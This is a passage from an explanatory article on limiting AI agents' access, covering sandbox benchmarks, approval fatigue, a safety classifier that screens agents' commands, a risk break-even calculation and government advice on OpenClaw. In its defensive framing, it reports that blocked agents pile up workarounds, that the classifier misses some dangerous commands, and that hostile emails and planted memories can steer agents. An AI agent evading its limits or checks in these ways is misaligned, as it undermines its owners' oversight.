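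An operator who already runs the agent from a standard account has therefore accepted the limit that reduces success the most, and adding an outbound allowlist and read-only folders may reduce it only a little more. These extra limits can still make the agent more expensive to run. Running all 89 tasks with Grok 4.5 in Grok Build cost $46 without limits, $82 without administrator rights and $123 under the strictest policy.

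Seven tasks became impossible under the strictest policy. Six required the agent to write to protected system folders, and the seventh needed a file from Hugging Face, a model- and data-sharing site that wasn't on the list of permitted domains. These seven account for about half of the average loss. On the other 82 tasks, the success rate fell from 72.5% to 65.1%.

The researchers also checked whether each task's official solution still worked under the strictest policy. It did for 50 tasks, and on those the agents' success fell by only 2 points, which could be chance. The other 32 tasks were still possible but needed a different method. On those, success fell from 70.3% to 54.5% and the average cost rose to 2.6 times the original. Before adopting a tighter limit, an operator can similarly try a typical task in the usual way under that limit and note what fails.

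Blocked agents ran out of time and gave wrong answers more often, but they still rarely stopped early. In a close reading of runs on two of the tasks, the researchers attributed nearly all the extra cost to workarounds, such as building a program from source after failing to install it. One run in the main test made 171 blocked connection attempts. Telling an agent about its limits in advance might avoid some of this, though the researchers didn't test that. A spending cap with the model provider is a more reliable way to control the bill.

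### Why a personal assistant may differ

The largest loss in Boundary-Bench may hardly affect a personal assistant. Installing and compiling software often requires administrator rights, while reading mail and writing drafts don't.

However, the test left out the limits that matter most for an assistant. It had no mailboxes or calendars, so it couldn't measure how much a narrower permission scope would reduce an assistant's usefulness. The file restrictions prevented changes but not reading. The 205 permitted domains included GitHub and large parts of Google's and Amazon's clouds, while the mail agent described earlier needed only four destinations. The strictest policy in the benchmark was therefore much looser than the one an owner might want for private mail.

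The scoring also doesn't reflect how people use an assistant. A coding task passes or fails, but a good draft is still mostly useful if the owner has to send it themselves. Davidovich and colleagues measured only the drawbacks of the limits, not how many attacks they would stop.

### What an approval prompt asks of the owner

With approval prompts, the agent keeps its permissions and the owner confirms each use, which seems to avoid the trade-off. OpenClaw's prompts are off by default, so most of the evidence comes from Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent. According to Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts*, Claude Code could originally read files freely but had to ask before changing one or running most commands. A few harmless commands, such as `echo`, needed no approval.

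The approval prompt usually shows the command, which may reveal little about what it will do. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analyses 290 reports of agents damaging files. In 80 cases the user had turned on automatic approval, and in 31 the prompt didn't give enough information for a sensible decision. For example, `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it runs whatever code is in that file.

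A programmer can open the file before deciding whether to allow an agent's command. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* argues that an office worker shouldn't have to make that judgment, so the company initially ran Cowork, its agent for general office work, inside a virtual machine with fixed limits. The same argument applies to most people who would want an agent's help with their email.

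### Why people wave prompts through

Frequent approval prompts interrupt people and take up time that the agent was supposed to save. One programmer in *Let the Agent Do It?* (Salerno, Gao and colleagues, 2026) said that having to click every ten seconds defeats the purpose. People then stop reading the prompts, a problem researchers call approval fatigue.

Anthropic reported in May that Claude Code users approved about 93% of permission prompts, and by August the rate was 97%. Most requests are harmless, so these rates don't prove that people were careless. Users also rejected 39% of the plans that Claude Code proposed before starting work, which shows that they object when they have something meaningful to review.

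Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports a controlled test of 1,053 paid testers who thought they were taking part in a general coding study. Once in each session, a prompt showed a clearly dangerous command, and only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. About 17% refused when it appeared early in a session, compared with about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

Anthropic's automatic classifier, a program that checks each action before it runs, blocked 89% of the same commands. The testers stopped only six that the classifier had missed, so using both would hardly have improved the result. Anthropic was promoting the classifier. The testers also had none of their own files at stake, so real owners may be more careful, but they would have to be much more careful to match the classifier.

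The classifier is now the default in Claude Code on most plans, and Anthropic says that business customers who adopted it produce about 25% more code changes. The classifier may not have caused the increase, since teams that adopt new tools early may already have been speeding up. The classifier missed 11% of the dangerous commands, and Anthropic recommends that people review high-stakes changes themselves.

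A sandbox also reduces the number of prompts, by letting commands inside it run without asking. The owner gets a prompt only when the agent tries to go beyond the boundary. In Anthropic's internal use, this cut prompts by 84%. With that reduction, an owner who used to get 50 prompts a day would get eight. The drawback is maintenance, because someone has to configure the sandbox for each new capability, as Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* points out.

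Without such help, users remove permission prompts on their own. By June, about half of Claude Code's active command-line users had written a rule that let some commands run without asking them. Many of these rules covered a whole programming language, such as Python, which in practice permits almost anything. A quarter of interactive sessions started with prompts turned off.

### What people say they would grant and what they approve

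Salerno and colleagues interviewed 18 software practitioners and surveyed 115. In the survey, 58.9% said they would never give an agent access to email or other personal information, and 56.1% would never give it administrator rights. A third had become less careful about prompts over time, and 20.6% approved requests by default. These people mostly used coding agents, which don't need a mailbox, so they lost little by refusing access to email.

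The closest study to personal assistants is *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026). It had 113 people from outside the software industry supervise a simulated assistant through a day of email, calendar and travel tasks. Seven of the assistant's 18 actions went beyond what the user had asked for. One group approved or refused each action. A second group first set a rule of "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four kinds of action, such as spending money or deleting something, and then saw prompts only for actions whose rule was "ask". A third group had a model screen the actions first.

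| Action outside the task | Approved by people asked about every action | Approved by people whose own rule was "ask" |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Call the airport to confirm a flight | 88% | 100% |
| Read private messages | 35% | 74% |
| Buy a $25 lounge pass | 32% | 61% |
| Permanently delete an old timesheet | 35% | 59% |
| Post publicly that the user is travelling | 21% | 48% |

The right-hand column leaves out people who had chosen "never", which makes the approval rates look worse. But the group with rules also did worse overall, blocking about 40% of the unwanted actions compared with 60% for people who decided every time. The group with rules did worse because 81% of its rules were "ask", and its members then approved two thirds of the unwanted actions they saw.

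The groups weren't perfectly comparable, because Yan assigned some later participants only to the group with rules. Participants also had no real money or messages at stake. Still, the study suggests that "ask" is a poor choice for actions the agent never needs to take. The few "never" rules blocked 31 unwanted actions without anyone having to notice them.

An owner can keep approval prompts useful by reserving them for a few serious actions. IMDA suggests requiring approval before an agent makes payments, deletes critical data, runs code on live systems or sends messages outside an organisation. The prompt for an email should show the recipient, the full text and any attachments. Software outside the model has to enforce the pause, as Summer Yue's case showed. IMDA also recommends testing the agent by asking it to clean up a folder and checking that it shows a preview and waits before deleting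 anything.

### A break-even calculation

Suppose an owner is choosing between giving an agent full access to a mailbox and letting it only write drafts. The figures are invented. Full access saves time worth $600 a year, but a serious incident would cost $20,000. Drafts-only access is worth $400 a year, and an incident would cost only $5,000 because the agent can't send or delete anything.

If *p* is the chance of a serious incident in a year, the expected yearly values are:

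- Full access: 600 − 20,000*p*
- Drafts only: 400 − 5,000*p*

Full access and drafts-only access are equally good when 15,000*p* = 200, so *p* is about 1.3%. Full access is better when *p* is lower than that.

| Yearly chance of an incident | Full access | Drafts only | Best choice |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| 0.5% | $500 | $375 | Full access |
| 1% | $400 | $350 | Full access |
| 2% | $200 | $300 | Drafts only |
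| 5% | −$400 | $150 | Drafts only |
| 10% | −$1,400 | −$100 | No agent |

The calculation assumes the same chance of an incident in both cases, although an agent that can't send mail should have fewer incidents. Even if limiting the agent to drafts removed the risk completely, the break-even point would fall only to 1%.

The difference in usefulness matters more. If the owner finds that sending drafts by hand takes $50 worth of time a year instead of $200, full access makes sense only below about 0.33%.

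### Why nobody knows the real probability

Nobody knows how many people run these agents or how many of those people suffer a serious loss. Counts of exposed gateways leave out private ones, and a victim may never discover that an agent leaked a document. Laboratory tests don't measure how many attacks will reach an agent. Criminals will probably attempt more attacks as agents become common, and a new model or a newly found flaw can suddenly change the risk.

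An owner's personal experience is also weak evidence about the risk, as are a few test emails that the agent resisted, because the samples are too small. Showing with 95% confidence that the yearly risk is below 1.3% would take about 225 owners with similar setups, all going a full year without a serious incident.

The average loss can also be the wrong basis for a decision. A 1% annual chance of losing $20,000 costs $200 a year on average, but someone without savings might sensibly pay more than $200 a year to avoid it.

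The example also leaves out harm to other people. A leaked mailbox contains messages from friends, clients and relatives. The gym customer who lost a waiting-list place and the maintainer an agent attacked had no say in how those agents were set up. If each incident did as much harm to other people as to the owner, the break-even point would halve to about 0.67%. Owners who count only their own losses will therefore tend to grant too much access.

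### The case for accepting the risk

In a post on OpenClaw's website responding to *Agents of Chaos*, Peter Steinberger writes that a single machine with one trusted user, such as a laptop or a Mac mini, was fine as it was. Most of the later hardening addressed threats that arise when several people share an agent, which most users never face, and some of it left ordinary users with fewer features.

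Steinberger also argues that the number of security reports exaggerates the danger. By 30 April, the project had received 1,309 reports and closed 746 as invalid. It had closed 95 of the 109 that claimed to be critical. Many described intended behavior, such as the agent running commands. But the project published 535, so real flaws were also common.

Users who accept the risk can reasonably object that an assistant isn't very useful without access to their mail and files. *The OpenClaw experiment is a warning shot for enterprise AI security*, from the security company Sophos, partly supports this objection. It warns that experienced organisations will struggle to secure the software "while still retaining any productivity value". Sophos treats this as a reason for caution, but an owner could equally see it as a reason to accept some risk.

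Anthropic, which sells agents, similarly argues that as agents become able to do the work of a person or a team, people lose more by not using them. The company now routinely gives Claude enough access to take down an internal service, a level of access it would have rejected a year earlier. But it also limits how much damage an agent can do.

### The case for isolation or no deployment

Microsoft's *Running OpenClaw safely* (February 2026) advises against running OpenClaw on an ordinary personal or work computer. It recommends that anyone who needs to evaluate the agent use a separate machine or virtual machine, accounts created for the agent and only non-sensitive data. Microsoft concludes that the right decision for most environments "may be not to deploy it".

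Microsoft also recommends rebuilding the agent's machine regularly and keeping a backup of the workspace folder, which doesn't include credentials. An owner should inspect that backup before restoring it, because an attacker may have planted a false memory in it.

The security teams' best reply to Steinberger is that attacks through hostile emails and malicious skills also work on a single-owner machine, as Android Authority's test showed for email.

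Microsoft's advice predates many of OpenClaw's security fixes, and the company sells products for monitoring such software. By June it was also helping people run agents. Its *Windows platform security for AI agents* (2026) announced several kinds of containment so that developers could match restrictions to the risk of the work.

Forrester advises companies to be very conservative by default, allow limited trials on separate machines with separate accounts, and require approval before an agent sends external email or deletes data. It also sensibly tells them to educate enthusiasts instead of just blocking them, since an employee who runs an agent secretly will probably have weaker protection than one in an approved trial.

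### What governments advise

Government advice is mostly cautious, though none of the guidance here amounts to a general ban. On 12 February, the Dutch data protection authority warned of data breaches and account takeovers, according to PPC Land's *Dutch authority flags open-source AI agents as a Trojan horse for hackers*. MLex's *Autonomous AI agents expose users to cyber dangers, Dutch data watchdog warns* (2026) adds that the authority told people and companies to keep such agents off sensitive systems.

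China's national computer emergency team warned on 10 March that poor installation and use had already caused serious security problems (CGTN, 2026). China Daily's *Guidelines released to curb OpenClaw security risks* describes advice for individuals to use a dedicated device, a virtual machine or a properly isolated container, avoid administrator rights and keep sensitive personal data out of OpenClaw. In Hong Kong, HKCERT (2026) told organisations to review software versions, third-party components and permissions together.

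On 1 May, the US agency CISA (2026) released guidance with agencies from Australia, Britain, Canada and New Zealand. It was the five countries' first joint guidance on AI agents, according to Crowell & Moring's *American and Allied Cyber Agencies Issue First Joint Guidance* (2026). In a passage quoted in Autokaam's *Five Eyes Guts Agentic Rollouts, Bleeds the Productivity Pitch*, the agencies tell organisations to put "resilience, reversibility and risk containment over efficiency gains" until security practices and standards mature.

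Singapore gives the most balanced advice. The Cyber Security Agency of Singapore's *Advisory on Cybersecurity Risks of OpenClaw* (2026) acknowledges both productivity benefits and serious risks. The Infocomm Media Development Authority (IMDA) says that a personal assistant needs autonomy and broad access to be helpful, and that people should accept the resulting risk deliberately, not through settings nobody checked. It suggests letting agents do low-risk work alone and requiring approval for anything serious or irreversible.

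An owner can fairly object that advice to avoid sensitive data rules out a mail assistant, since almost any mailbox contains some. Governments can reply that they are advising millions of people whose skills and circumstances they can't check, many of whom will never change a default setting. Governments also have to consider the harm to others, which many owners will underestimate.

Much of this disagreement disappears if the agent has full control of a spare machine and its own accounts. This setup meets most of Microsoft's conditions and still lets the agent install software, run for hours and make mistakes that the owner can erase. Broad access there is usually worth the risk, as long as the agent can't publish or message outsiders without review.

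The owner's main mailbox is a harder case because the sensitive data is the reason for connecting it. The uncertainty favours starting with read access and drafts. For a month, the owner can then note each time the limit got in the way and how long the extra step took. These notes replace the invented $200 with a real figure. If most of the delays come from one routine message, such as a weekly report to the same colleague, the owner can let the agent send that message to that address and keep the rest as drafts.
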